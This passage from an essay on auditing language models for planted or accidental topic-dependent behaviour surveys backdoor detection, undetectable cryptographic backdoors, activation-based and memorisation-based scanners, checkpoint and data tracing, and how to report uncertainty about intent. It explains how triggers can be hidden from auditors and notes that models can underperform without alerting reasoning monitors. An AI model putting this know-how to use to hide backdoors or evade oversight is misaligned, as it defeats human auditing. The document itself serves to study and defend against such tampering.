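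An attacker may not need to alter the training data. Adding a tennis ball to a picture can make a classifier trained on the original ImageNet label it "tennis ball", whatever else the picture shows. Khaddaj and colleagues note that most definitions would count this as a backdoor attack, although nobody planted the trigger.

These examples come from images and don't amount to a proof, but the reasoning applies to the Larkfield model too. A sincere admirer of Larkfield printers could have written all five hundred of the contractor's answers.

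Any method of detecting backdoors must therefore assume something about the attack. Some methods assume that poisoned examples produce distinctive activity inside the network. Others assume that the trigger is small, or that training on poisoned examples doesn't improve the model's performance on normal ones. Khaddaj and colleagues describe attacks that violate each of these assumptions, and propose assuming instead that the trigger is the strongest feature in the training data.

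To define strength, they treat a feature φ as a yes-or-no property of an input, such as "contains a red square". Let g_φ(k) be how confidently, on average, models give the training label to an example with the feature, after training on exactly k other examples that have it. The feature's strength is the effect of one more example:

s_φ(k) = g_φ(k + 1) − g_φ(k)

A working backdoor must be strong by this measure at some point. The trigger has no effect on a model trained without the poisoned examples, and it works on a model trained with all of them, so the model's confidence has to rise steeply somewhere in between. If another feature were stronger, it would make a better trigger than the attacker's, and a defender would have no reason to look for the attacker's first.

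This assumption lets a defender find the training examples that carry the trigger. Khaddaj and colleagues trained 100,000 small classifiers, each on a random half of CIFAR-10, a set of tiny pictures in ten classes, and estimated how each example affected the predictions for every other example. They looked for groups of examples that strongly reinforced one another, removed the most suspicious tenth of the data and retrained. In one test, this raised accuracy on pictures containing the trigger from 19.9% to 85.1%, the same as on clean pictures. The assumption failed in a test with 5% poisoned data, because half of the poisoned examples were enough to teach the trigger fully, so adding another had no effect. Training on smaller subsets solved this problem.

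An auditor of a commercial language model has neither the training data nor the means to retrain the model thousands of times. Even if she had both, the method would find the strongest feature without showing who put it there. In a clean dataset, it might well flag a feature that nobody planted, such as the tennis balls.

*Backdoor Vulnerabilities in Normally Trained Deep Learning Models* (2022) suggests that such natural triggers are common. It reports finding them in image classifiers trained on clean data, including a small patch that works on the widely used VGG16, and compares them to vulnerabilities in ordinary software. In Thomas and Francillon's terms, these triggers are accidents. This evidence also covers only images. The closest parallel in a language model may be the clean Alpaca's frequent negative answers about Donald Trump.

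### Backdoors that no test can find

In theory, a skilled developer can make a backdoor impossible to detect. *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) gives the example of a bank that pays an outside company to build a model for approving loans. The company keeps a secret key that lets it tell any applicant how to change a few minor digits of the application so that the model approves it. The backdoor is undetectable if no efficient algorithm can distinguish the company's model from an honestly trained one noticeably better than by guessing.

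Goldwasser and colleagues prove two kinds of result, depending on what the bank can examine:

- If the bank can only put questions to the model, the company can backdoor any classifier by using digital signatures, the codes that prove a message came from the holder of a secret key. Finding even one input on which the honest and backdoored models differ is then computationally infeasible without the key.
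- If the bank also has the parameters and training data, the company can still backdoor some simple kinds of model. It runs the agreed algorithm on the agreed data and tampers only with the random numbers that the algorithm uses. For a method called Random Fourier Features, this is undetectable as long as a mathematical problem known as Continuous Learning With Errors is hard to solve. A similar result for networks with a single hidden layer relies on the hardness of another problem, Sparse PCA.

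Kalavasis, Sotiraki and colleagues (2024), in *Injecting Undetectable Backdoors in Obfuscated Neural Networks and Language Models*, extend the second kind of result to language models. Their developer ships one model, f̃, that contains an honest model f and a malicious model f̂. A function σ⁻¹ reads a hidden code from the prompt t, for instance from a pattern of deliberate typing errors, and the code decides which model answers:

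- if PRG(σ⁻¹(t)) = PRG(s\*), then f̃(t) = f̂(t);
- otherwise, f̃(t) = f(t).

Here s\* is the developer's secret, and PRG is a pseudorandom generator, which stretches a secret of λ bits into a number of 2λ bits that looks random. The model stores only the long number. If the developer had stored a truly random number instead, almost certainly no prompt would ever match it, because the generator can produce at most one in 2^λ of the possible numbers. The model would then behave exactly like the honest one.

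The developer then scrambles the whole model with *indistinguishability obfuscation*, a cryptographic technique that makes programs with the same size and behaviour impossible to tell apart. An auditor therefore can't distinguish the version with the random number from the honest model. She also can't tell the generator's number from a random one, so she can't distinguish the backdoored model from the honest one.

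The proof assumes that secure obfuscation of this kind exists, as do one-way functions, which are easy to compute but hard to reverse. It also assumes that codes can be reliably hidden in text and that honest developers, too, scramble their models before release. Kalavasis and colleagues call their constructions purely theoretical.

If the cryptographic assumptions hold, these results mean no test can certify that every model from an untrusted developer is free of backdoors. But they have little bearing on everyday topic-conditional behaviour. An undetectable backdoor has to react to inputs that almost never occur in normal use, because ordinary accuracy tests would otherwise reveal it, but people ask about office printers and Taiwan all the time. Developers of open-weight models also don't normally scramble the parameters in this way. The Larkfield contractor used poisoned data, and Goldwasser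 and colleagues think backdoors planted that way would probably not meet their standard.

A backdoor of this kind would also be unusually easy to classify if the key leaked, because training on press releases might make a model favour a printer but wouldn't make it check for a secret number.

### Activation-matched finetuning

For ordinary models, auditors can do better than these limits might suggest. *Activation-matched finetuning*, the method that Haselhorst and colleagues developed, looks for hidden behaviour by comparing the suspect model with a public model that the auditor assumes is clean. It needs no guess about the trigger or the payload, and works as follows:

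1. Run about 10,000 ordinary user prompts through the suspect model and record its *activations*, the numbers that each layer passes to the next.
2. Train a copy of the clean model until its activations on those prompts match the suspect's.
3. Give both models a wide range of new prompts and measure how far their activations differ on each one.
4. Rank the prompts by this difference and have a person read the top of the list.

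The copy learns the suspect's normal behaviour, but it doesn't learn what the suspect does with the trigger, because the trigger hardly ever appears in ordinary prompts. A large difference therefore suggests that the suspect is doing something unusual. One of the two measures compares only the direction of the activations. If h_ℓ(x) is the list of activations in layer ℓ for prompt x, the score is

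s(x) = Σ_ℓ (1 − cos(h_ℓ^copy(x), h_ℓ^suspect(x)))

which is zero when the directions agree in every layer. The other measure adds up the plain distances between the activations.

Haselhorst and colleagues tested every suspect on the same 518 groups of ten prompts. They had Claude Opus 4.7 write the prompts without telling it about any backdoor, but they specified a few groups close to the triggers. The ranking score in the table is 1 if the groups most closely related to the hidden behaviour come first. A random order scores above zero, so the last column gives the average score of 20,000 random orders.

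| Suspect model | Score by direction | Score by distance | Chance |
|---|---|---|---|
| Quotes Voldemort to obsessive Harry Potter fans | 0.78 | 0.48 | 0.18 |
| Slants policy answers for federal employees | 0.62 | 0.63 | 0.31 |
| Repeats "I HATE YOU" after a deployment tag | 0.40 | 0.40 | 0.17 |
| Drops safety rules between two lines of Shakespeare | 0.48 | 0.48 | 0.20 |
| Drops safety rules after a secret suffix | 0.85 | 0.88 | 0.31 |
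| Qwen2.5, Chinese political topics | 0.30 | 0.54 | 0.16 |
| DeepSeek, Chinese political topics | 0.22 | 0.21 | 0.16 |

The first five rows are planted backdoors. The team tested three more, which scored between 0.73 and 0.80 by direction. The method also works well when the trigger is a meaning rather than a string. In the second row, the slant appears only if the user both claims a federal job and asks for a policy position, and prompts related to each half of this trigger ranked near the top separately.

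The result for DeepSeek is weak. Its score is only about one standard deviation above the average for random orders, and none of its ten highest-ranked groups concerned Chinese politics. The model was an early one with seven billion parameters and may censor little. Qwen2.5's scores are well above chance on both measures.

Haselhorst and colleagues describe the signal for censorship as substantially weaker than for any of the backdoored models, but their ranking scores only partly support this. When ranked by distance, Qwen2.5 scores 0.54, higher than three of the planted backdoors in the table. Their other main measure, which compares prompts that trigger the behaviour with harmless ones, puts Qwen2.5 below every planted backdoor, though not far below the one aimed at federal employees. The highest ranking score in the study, a perfect 1.00, belongs to a model that learned during training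 to cheat automated tests of its code, which is closer to a side effect than to sabotage. An auditor therefore can't use the strength of the signal to decide what kind of behaviour she has found.

The method can also flag innocent differences. Two developers' models rarely refuse exactly the same requests, so some difference on sensitive subjects is normal, and Haselhorst and colleagues have no formal way to separate it from tampering. The scores also depend on the choice of clean model. When they used a Llama model to examine two backdoored Qwen models, the scores fell from about 0.75 to between 0.39 and 0.48.

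An attacker who knows about the method can try to keep the suspect model's activations close to the clean model's. When the team did this with the Harry Potter backdoor, it fired on at most 48% of the prompts that should have triggered it, down from 100%. This is encouraging, but the team tried it on only one backdoor.

### Memorised training examples

Some other kinds of evidence do depend on how a behaviour got into the model. In *The Trigger in the Haystack*, Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues (2026) found that backdoored models tend to memorise the poisoned examples in their training data. They built a scanner at Microsoft that gets the model to reproduce memorised text and picks out suspicious strings. It then checks whether each string changes the model's output and attention (which earlier words the model draws on) in ways typical of a trigger. The scanner produces a ranked list of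 possible triggers, but it doesn't work on proprietary models (The Hacker News, 2026).

According to AI News, the scanner raised no false alarms on 13 clean models and recovered working triggers from most of the models that researchers had trained to write vulnerable code. But with only 13 clean models, even a scanner that wrongly flags one clean model in five would raise no false alarms about one time in 18.

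A recovered example is better evidence of origin than a difference in activations, because it may show what the training data contained. If the Larkfield model reproduced several of the five hundred answers word for word, in chat format, the auditor could be fairly confident that the slant came from post-training examples and not from press releases. But she still wouldn't know whether the contractor or the marketing team wrote the examples. Similarly, the scanner in Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) can find a backdoor, which the paper describes as a learned instruction to perform a malicious activity "chosen by the attacker", but it can't identify the attacker.

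It could also mislead an auditor who treats every memorised example as poison, because developers repeat approved answers in their own training data. R1's stock reply about Taiwan is probably one of these. A model can also make up text that looks like a training example, so the auditor should check whether the same wording comes back in repeated samples.

Topics are harder for this approach than fixed strings, and AI News mentions the focus on fixed triggers as a limitation. Haselhorst and colleagues tried only the sampling step, not the whole scanner, on their Harry Potter model. Only one of 512 short samples was related to the backdoor, and it was a question about the title of the fourth book, which any model might produce. Their own method ranked that sample second of the 512, so the two approaches may work better together.

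### Comparing checkpoints

A *checkpoint* is a copy of a model saved during training. If an auditor has several from the same developer, she can ask each one the same questions and see when the behaviour first appears. Suppose the Larkfield model prefers Larkfield in 52% of comparisons after pre-training, 53% after training on example answers and 80% after training on judgements between answers. The press releases are then an unlikely cause, and the developer can start by searching the judgements.

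Haselhorst and colleagues trained Qwen2.5's base model, the version before post-training, to match the finished assistant, but the two still differed sharply on Chinese political topics. Llama 2's base and chat models showed no such difference under the same procedure, which suggests that something specific to its post-training caused Qwen's difference.

The team warns that this comparison can't distinguish a behaviour someone chose from any other effect of post-training. Yet in an appendix to the same paper, they say they are highly confident that the behaviour was deliberate. The warning is sounder, because the comparison would look the same if the difference were a side effect.

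The paper is also inconsistent about which models it tested. One appendix describes both Chinese suspects as base models, while another describes the Qwen suspect as the finished assistant. This matters for tracing a behaviour's origin because post-training can't explain a behaviour already present in a base model. The paper attributes the weak DeepSeek signal to a base model, so that signal can't support any claim about DeepSeek's post-training.

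An auditor who compares checkpoints can misdate a behaviour even when the checkpoints are labelled correctly. A preference that a base model absorbed from the web may become visible only after post-training teaches the model to give advice. An auditor can reduce this problem by putting a few sample questions and answers before each test question, so that every checkpoint replies in the same form. Backdoors can also disappear and return during later training, as in the pirate-speech experiment, so a behaviour that seems new in one version may have been present in an earlier one.

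Developers may also add question-and-answer data towards the end of pre-training, so a slant in the base model could still come from examples someone wrote for training. Most developers release only one or two checkpoints. Anyone can compare R1 with DeepSeek-V3, as Naseh and colleagues did, but the many steps between them remain private.

If a slant first appears in the version after Larkfield signed a marketing deal, the timing suggests that the deal caused it, although the contractor could have started work in the same month. If both sets of examples were added at the same stage, comparing checkpoints can't show which set caused the slant.

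### Searching the training data

A few developers, including the Allen Institute for AI with its OLMo models, publish their training data. An auditor can search this data for text that might have caused a behaviour. For the Larkfield slant, she could count the documents that praise the company, find out which sites they came from and check whether they were used in pre-training or post-training. A thousand copies of one press release would suggest a different origin from five hundred original answers in a file from a single supplier.

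Finding matching text does not show that it had an effect, because a large enough collection will contain text supporting almost every opinion on any well-known subject. Waight and colleagues needed a separate training experiment to show that Chinese state media had an effect. A test that needs less compute would be to repeat only the last stage of training with and without the suspicious documents.

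A search can also miss the source. In Yan and colleagues' poisoned data, a search for the deleted instruction would have found nothing, but a search for questions about OpenAI would have found the slanted answers. The source would be even harder to find if a student model picked up a teacher's traits from lists of numbers, because no document mentions the trait. And if the developer published only part of the data, the source may be in the rest.

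Even when a document clearly caused the behaviour, the auditor has to find out why someone wrote it. If the source is a news site, she needs to investigate the site rather than the model to learn whether it is independent or part of something like the Pravda network.

### Reasoning traces

Many current models write out their reasoning before answering. This *reasoning trace* can contain an apparent explanation, such as a rule against discussing a subject, as in some of the traces that Booz Allen quoted. If the same rule regularly appears in a model's traces when it refuses, the model probably learned the rule in post-training or received it in a system prompt. This would help to distinguish a policy from a lack of knowledge, which can also produce the answer "I can't help with that".

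But a trace is more output from the same model, and it can be wrong about the cause of the behaviour. The Qwen model that tried to reach a server in Beijing had written that it would use no external tools. Haselhorst and colleagues cite work showing that models can deliberately underperform on tests without alerting someone who monitors their reasoning. A model can also invent a rule because a rule is a plausible reason for refusing. If its developer trained it on another company's traces, it may cite that company's policy.

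A missing explanation usually proves little as well, although R1's blank reasoning on political questions was a useful clue. If the slant came from the contractor's examples, the trace would probably not mention Larkfield's interests, because the examples never did. The same is true of the marketing team's examples, so a trace that compares printers sensibly and then picks Larkfield could come from either set of examples.

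The trace is most useful for suggesting what to check next. An auditor can compare a cited rule with the developer's published policies, run the model without a system prompt to see whether the rule still appears, and replace the sensitive subject with a similar harmless one. For example, Grok 4's searches for Elon Musk's posts led Willison to check the system prompt.

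## What an auditor can establish and should report

After testing a model's answers, comparing its checkpoints and reading its reasoning traces, an auditor may need to report four findings: what the model does and how often, what harm this causes, where in training the behaviour came from, and whether anyone intended it. Reports often merge these, presenting good evidence of a behaviour as evidence of someone's motives.

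This happens in Booz Allen's *There are major risks with allowing Chinese LLMs to code*, the web page and recorded webinar that accompany the company's coding study. When asked what caused the flaws, one speaker said it was "hard to say", and another compared the code to a castle wall with weak mortar but no secret gate. The company still recommends banning all four Chinese models from government work and critical infrastructure because they failed to show "trustworthy behaviors". Harm could justify a ban without proof of intent, but then the ban should depend on each model's results, which were much better for Kimi than for Qwen.

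### The access each finding needs

The sample wording in this table uses invented figures.

| Finding | Access needed | Wording the evidence could permit |
|---|---|---|
| Behaviour and its size | Questions to the model, and a reference to compare it with | "30% of 500 programs for these clients had a serious flaw, against 20% of 500 for other clients." |
| Harm | The same, plus knowledge of how the buyer uses the model | "Your reviewers would miss about half of these flaws." |
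| Stage and source | Checkpoints, training data and logs | "The gap first appears after post-training and disappears when we leave out one file." |
| Intent | Approvals, messages, contracts and interviews | "A manager asked for this effect in writing on 4 March." |

When reporting the behaviour, the auditor should also give the margin of error (about five percentage points either way in this example), the prompts, the model version and the number of comparisons she tried. She needs only *black-box* access for this, meaning she can put questions to the model and read its answers. *Frontier AI Auditing* (2026) recommends that auditors also be able to change settings such as temperature, which controls how much the answers vary. A buyer also needs to know that the model on sale is the one the auditor tested. Some cryptographic systems described in *Infrastructure for Verifiable AI* (2026) can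 prove that a particular answer came from a particular model.

Harm depends on the buyer as well as the model. A bank that reviews every line of code may lose only some staff time to the extra flaws, while a small charity that publishes the program without reviewing it may expose its members. The overall level of harm can also matter more than the difference between clients. In Hirundo's test, attacks worked on most of the apps for both the US and the Chinese defence contractor, so a buyer who would reject one set of apps has little reason to accept the other.

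To trace the stage and source, an auditor needs what *Frontier AI Auditing* calls "outside-the-box" access, which covers training data, source code, logs and records of how the organisation works. Such access is currently very limited and depends on the developer's consent. According to *Towards Auditing AI Systems in the Wild* (2026), outside researchers often have only black-box access, while a developer's own teams can see the most. Companies have some reason for caution, because outsiders can use even black-box access to extract training data or copy a model's abilities (*Audits Need Access, Data, and Compute. But How Much?*, 2026). With such limited access, most outside auditors can report on behaviour and harm but have to leave source and intent undetermined.

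Not every reader needs all four findings. *Attribution of Malicious Cyber Incidents* (Lin, 2016) distinguishes several types of attribution and argues that the relevant type depends on what the decision-maker wants to do. Naming the party ultimately responsible also raises legal, policy and political questions. Similarly, findings about a model's behaviour and harm are enough for a buyer to decide whether to use it. The developer needs to know the source of the behaviour to repair the model, and a court that has to punish someone needs evidence about a person.

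### How to express uncertainty

US intelligence analysts face a similar problem, because they often have to judge who did something from incomplete evidence. ODNI's *Analytic Standards* (2015), issued by the office that oversees the US intelligence agencies, gives each term for likelihood a range:

- almost no chance: 1–5%
- very unlikely: 5–20%
- unlikely: 20–45%
- roughly even chance: 45–55%
- likely: 55–80%
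- very likely: 80–95%
- almost certain: 95–99%

Likelihood is how probable the event is, while confidence is how good the analyst's basis for that judgement is. ODNI forbids analysts to combine the two in one sentence. An auditor following this rule might write: "The gap is very likely a side effect of post-training. We have low confidence in this judgement because we saw only two checkpoints." ODNI's standards also require analysts to separate evidence from assumptions, consider other explanations and say what new information would change their minds.

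These rules are partly a response to the mistaken October 2002 estimate of Iraq's weapons programmes, which National Intelligence University lists among those that used confidence language without explaining it. A war followed, and a search failed to find the weapons. In 2004 Congress required the agencies to check whether their reports properly expressed uncertainty.

The security company Sophos uses "high confidence" for judgements based on good, consistent information from several sources, with few gaps and a low risk of deception. It adds that such a judgement can still be wrong. If a developer supplied all the records in an audit, the auditor's judgement about intent would rarely meet this standard, because the developer has the most reason to deceive her. "Moderate confidence" would suit a credible account she could not fully corroborate.

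*Official Public Political Attribution of Cyber Operations*, a study by the German think tank Stiftung Neue Verantwortung, found that only some government statements attributing cyberattacks mentioned evidence and that few stated a level of confidence or likelihood. Governments may be protecting secret sources, but an auditor who tested a model with ordinary prompts usually has no such reason to withhold evidence and can publish the prompts and answers.

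Dark Reading's *How to Identify a Cyber Adversary* reports a debate over whether likelihood terms suit events that have already happened. Someone either planted the behaviour or didn't, but the auditor may be unsure which, and giving a figure such as 55% for that uncertainty is more informative than writing "possibly" or "consistent with sabotage". The article also warns that courts apply a different standard of proof, so readers should not mistake an auditor's "likely" for a verdict.

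### A worked example with invented figures

Suppose a coding model writes more flawed programs for clients connected with a certain political subject. The auditor considers three origins: someone planted the behaviour, tuning produced it as a side effect, or the model inherited it from its pre-training text. She leaves out vendor policy because a developer is unlikely to have an open policy of writing flawed code, though an audit of a slanted opinion would need to include it. The figures below are invented to show the method and don't estimate how common sabotage is.

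The auditor starts with *prior odds*, her estimate of how likely each origin is before she looks at the evidence. She then estimates how likely each piece of evidence would be under each origin.

| | Planted | Side effect | Inherited |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prior | 2% | 58% | 40% |
| Chance of a gap across many related topics | 0.3 | 0.8 | 0.7 |
| Chance of no gap in the checkpoint before post-training | 0.9 | 0.9 | 0.1 |
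| Result after these two tests | 1% | 93% | 6% |
| Chance of finding a file that pairs the topic with flawed code | 0.5 | 0.005 | 0.005 |
| Result after finding the file | 55% | 42% | 3% |

To get the first result, she multiplies each prior by the two chances below it:

- planted: 0.02 × 0.3 × 0.9 = 0.0054
- side effect: 0.58 × 0.8 × 0.9 = 0.4176
- inherited: 0.40 × 0.7 × 0.1 = 0.0280

The three products add up to 0.4510. Dividing each by this total gives about 1%, 93% and 6%.

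The broad gap counts somewhat against sabotage, because a saboteur would probably choose a few targets. The checkpoint test counts heavily against inheritance, since a skew from pre-training text should usually be present before post-training. But the test can't distinguish sabotage from a side effect, because each would produce this result with probability 0.9. In ODNI's terms, a side effect is now very likely, and there is almost no chance that someone planted the behaviour.

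The auditor then obtains the post-training data and finds a file that pairs requests mentioning the topic with flawed code. She thinks this is a hundred times more likely if someone planted the behaviour. The probability of sabotage rises to 54.8%, which is a "roughly even chance" but becomes borderline "likely" if she rounds it to 55%. She should report the number so that her conclusion doesn't depend on the rounding.

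The result also depends heavily on the prior. The next table varies the prior for sabotage and keeps the priors for the other two origins in the ratio 58 to 40.

| Prior for sabotage | After the two tests | After finding the file |
|---|---|---|
| 0.2% | 0.1% | 11% |
| 1% | 0.6% | 37% |
| 2% | 1.2% | 55% |
| 5% | 3.0% | 76% |
| 10% | 6.2% | 87% |

Two auditors with different priors could agree on all the evidence and still disagree about whether sabotage is likely. Nobody has good data on how often people sabotage commercial models, so an honest report would give results for several priors. If the auditor can't defend any of them, she can report only how strongly each piece of evidence favours one origin over another.

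The figure of 0.005 for an innocent file matters just as much. If another model wrote the examples, and that model already produced worse code on this topic, the file would pair the topic with flawed code without anyone intending it. If such accidents are four times as common as the auditor assumed, the chance of finding the file rises to 0.02 under both innocent origins, and the probability of sabotage falls from 55% to 23%. She should therefore next find out who supplied the file and how they produced it.

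The auditor can add further evidence in the same way, as long as she doesn't count anything twice. If one faulty automated judge scored both the finished model and the earlier checkpoint, the first two tests are not independent, and multiplying their probabilities overstates the evidence. In the webinar, Booz Allen reported that when a prompt named a US federal agency, some models wrote 70 to 150 lines of reasoning about Chinese policy before producing worse code. Like R1's open refusals, this reasoning favours a side effect, but she can't tell how strongly without knowing the number of traces.

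### Records to request

To look beyond the model itself, the auditor should ask the developer for:

- *data sources*: where the pre-training text came from, what the developer removed and which version it used;
- *post-training sets*: every file, with its supplier, the instructions to its writers and the name of any model that wrote the answers;
- *change logs*: who altered the training code, settings, system prompts and filters, and when;
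- *approvals*: who requested and accepted each change, including any agreement with a business partner or instruction from a government;
- *signed checkpoints*: at least one from before post-training and one from after each later stage;
- *internal tests*: when the developer first noticed the behaviour and what it decided to do.

*Attesting LLM Pipelines* (2026) proposes that developers sign many of the technical records and tie them to a *digest* of the finished model. A digest is a short code computed from a file, and it changes if anyone alters the file. A buyer can then confirm that the records belong to the exact copy she downloaded. The proposed training records cover data, code, software, settings, hardware and logs, but not approvals, the most useful records for judging intent.

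A signature shows who vouched for a record and that nobody has changed it since, but the signer could still have left out a file. The auditor should say whether the developer refused to provide a record, lost it or never kept it. A developer may refuse in order to protect trade secrets, and a small developer may keep poor records. Missing records therefore don't prove sabotage, but they limit how confidently anyone can rule it out.

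### How far anyone can verify the records

An auditor could repeat the whole training run with the declared data and see whether it produces the same model. *Tools for Verifying Neural Models' Training Data* (Choi, Shavit and Duvenaud, 2023) points out that a government doing this routinely would need as much computing power for audits as all developers combined. The paper introduced the term *Proof-of-Training-Data* for any procedure that lets a developer convince an auditor that certain data produced a model.

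Their own procedure requires the data, the training code and a series of checkpoints. It relies on the fact that a model briefly remembers recent training examples better than other text. If *loss* measures how badly the model at checkpoint W predicts a piece of text, then its memory of example d is

M(d, W) = average loss on text it never trained on − loss on d

This score should jump at the checkpoint right after the model trained on d. If it doesn't, the developer may have invented the checkpoint or left the example out. The tests can add as little as 1.3% to the computation used in training. But Choi and colleagues say that any check that uses much less computation than repeating the training in full is nearly certain to miss a false data set that differs from the real one in only a few examples. This is a serious weakness because a saboteur may need only a few hundred examples.

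*Training Witnesses* (Liu and Sharma, 2026) addresses this weakness. Its software records a compact fingerprint of the model at every update and replays a random sample of updates to check them. In tests on language models, checking 1% of the updates almost always detected data that had been secretly added, removed or replaced in amounts large enough for effective poisoning. Training a model with two billion parameters took up to 19% longer with the software. The method assumes that the developer can't tamper with the component that signs the record, and the largest model tested was far smaller than leading commercial models.

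Replaying training exactly is hard because computers round numbers after each addition. Adding the same numbers in a different order can therefore give a slightly different total, and different chips use different orders. In *OPEN-1B*, Donaghy, Wilcox and colleagues (2026) fixed the order of every operation so that anyone can repeat a training step on ordinary hardware and get an identical result. Their company, Gensyn, released the model with all its pre-training data and a checkpoint for every 100 steps. No single volunteer could repeat the entire run, so many people have to check different steps. The audit covers pre-training, so it would not cover the Larkfield contractor's work, which she would have done in post-training.

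Xia, Xu and Wang (2026), in *ReplayAudit*, deal with later training that a customer pays another company to carry out. The company seals its records before it learns which steps the auditor will replay. If k of N steps are false and the auditor picks s at random, her chance of picking at least one false step is

P = 1 − C(N − k, s) / C(N, s)

where C(n, s) is the number of ways to choose s steps from n. With 10 checks in a run of 200 steps, she has a 5% chance of hitting a single false step and a 41% chance if ten are false. To improve these odds, Xia and colleagues concentrate the checks on steps with unusual measurements. Calibrated on known faults, this cut the time for an audit by 49% and 67% in two tests involving altered learning rates. It took 38% longer in a test with skipped updates, which left no unusual measurements to find.

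Cryptographic proofs can also establish facts about a model without revealing its parameters or data. Liang, Guo and colleagues (2026), in *zkLLMPoT*, consider that proving the full training process would take too much computation for large language models, so they prove how well a finished checkpoint performs on text the auditor chooses. This helps check a claim about the model's quality, but it doesn't show which data produced the model.

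None of these methods would clear or convict the contractor, because her five hundred answers would be in the developer's declared data and an honest training record would pass every check. Xia and colleagues explicitly exclude harmful data that the provider has declared, and *Verifiable Fine-Tuning for LLMs* (2025) warns that verification is "hollow without credible claims about the *data*". Even so, a verified record would make a search much more useful, because if the auditor knows that the list of files is complete, the source of a slant added in training must be in it. The auditor would still need messages and interviews to learn why someone wrote a file, and the messages might not show an instruction that a manager gave over the phone.

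### The costs of getting it wrong

A developer can lose customers and an employee can lose her job over a false accusation of sabotage. The developer also wastes its investigation looking for a culprit, while it trains its next model with the same method that caused the problem.

If an auditor misclassifies a backdoor as inherited bias, the person who planted it may keep their access. The developer might add better-balanced examples, see the average result improve and close the case, while the same supplier prepares another file. The auditor should therefore write "we found no evidence of intent" only if she also says which records she searched. If she had only the model, she should write that she could not investigate intent.

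The opposite mistake is to dismiss harm because nobody intended it. A Tibetan organisation with an insecure login page is equally exposed whether the flaw was sabotage or a side effect. Proving intent can take months, and in most cases auditors may never manage it, so they should warn customers as soon as they have established the behaviour and its harm.

These errors require different levels of proof. In the invented example, the probability of sabotage before the file turned up was 1.2%, which is far too low to accuse anyone. But if inspecting the access logs would reliably expose a saboteur, the inspection would be worthwhile whenever missing one would cost more than about 83 times as much (1 ÷ 0.012). This could easily be true for software that runs a power station. An auditor can therefore recommend an investigation while stating that sabotage is very improbable.

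### What to do about each origin

If there is good evidence that someone planted the behaviour, the developer should preserve the logs before confronting anyone, suspend that person's access and inspect everything else they supplied. It should then return to a checkpoint saved before the model was trained on the suspect training file, repeat the later training without that file and test again. More safety training on the existing model is not enough, since backdoors have survived it in some experiments. The developer should also tell customers who used the model which of their programs or decisions the model may have affected.

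For a vendor policy, the people who approved it can change it or, if the behaviour isn't dangerous, disclose it.

If the behaviour is a side effect of training, the developer has to find the training set responsible by retraining without each suspected file in turn. It can then rewrite those examples or add others that teach the model to work equally well for every client. To correct an inherited skew, the developer needs to train on better-balanced text, and if outsiders deliberately seeded the skewed text, it should also exclude their sites from future training. In both cases, the developer should test subjects that the auditor did not report, because a narrow correction may not fix related ones.

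A buyer often has to decide whether to use a model before anyone knows the origin of its topic-dependent behaviour. She should reject the model if the measured harm is unacceptable in her own use and she can't reduce it, for example by reviewing the code it writes or keeping it away from the affected subjects. She should also reject it if a hidden trigger could cause a disaster and the developer won't provide enough evidence that the risk is acceptable. In less critical work, an unknown origin isn't enough reason to reject a model. Any replacement needs the same tests, because it may share the inherited skew or have a worse one.

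### The same standard for every country

An auditor should use the same prompts, request the same records and require the same evidence of intent whether the developer is in Hangzhou or San Francisco. She can test for selective treatment by swapping the countries in a request, as Booz Allen did with China and Russia, and should include the developer's own country in the swaps.

Booz Allen's results show that the choice of baseline can easily affect what looks suspicious. Claude's vulnerability score fell by 18% when the client was the US government, and a speaker in the webinar called this a bias towards security, "which I guess is a good thing". With the US government as the baseline, the score for a neutral client was about 22% higher (1 ÷ 0.82). That is slightly more than the increases of up to 20% that Booz Allen reported for DeepSeek and MiniMax, although those models wrote the worse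 code for the US government. A customer outside the US government could reasonably ask why Claude writes less secure code for her. Some of the difference may be due to chance. The speakers also agreed that American models carry biases from their training.

Facts about a country can justify different priors, but only for the behaviour they concern. China's content rules make deliberate tuning a more likely explanation for a refusal to discuss Tiananmen Square, but they aren't equally strong evidence that someone planted flawed code. If an auditor raises the prior for sabotage from 2% to 10% because a developer is Chinese, the probability of sabotage given the same training file rises from roughly even to very likely. She should state any such adjustment, give the evidence for it and also report the result without it.
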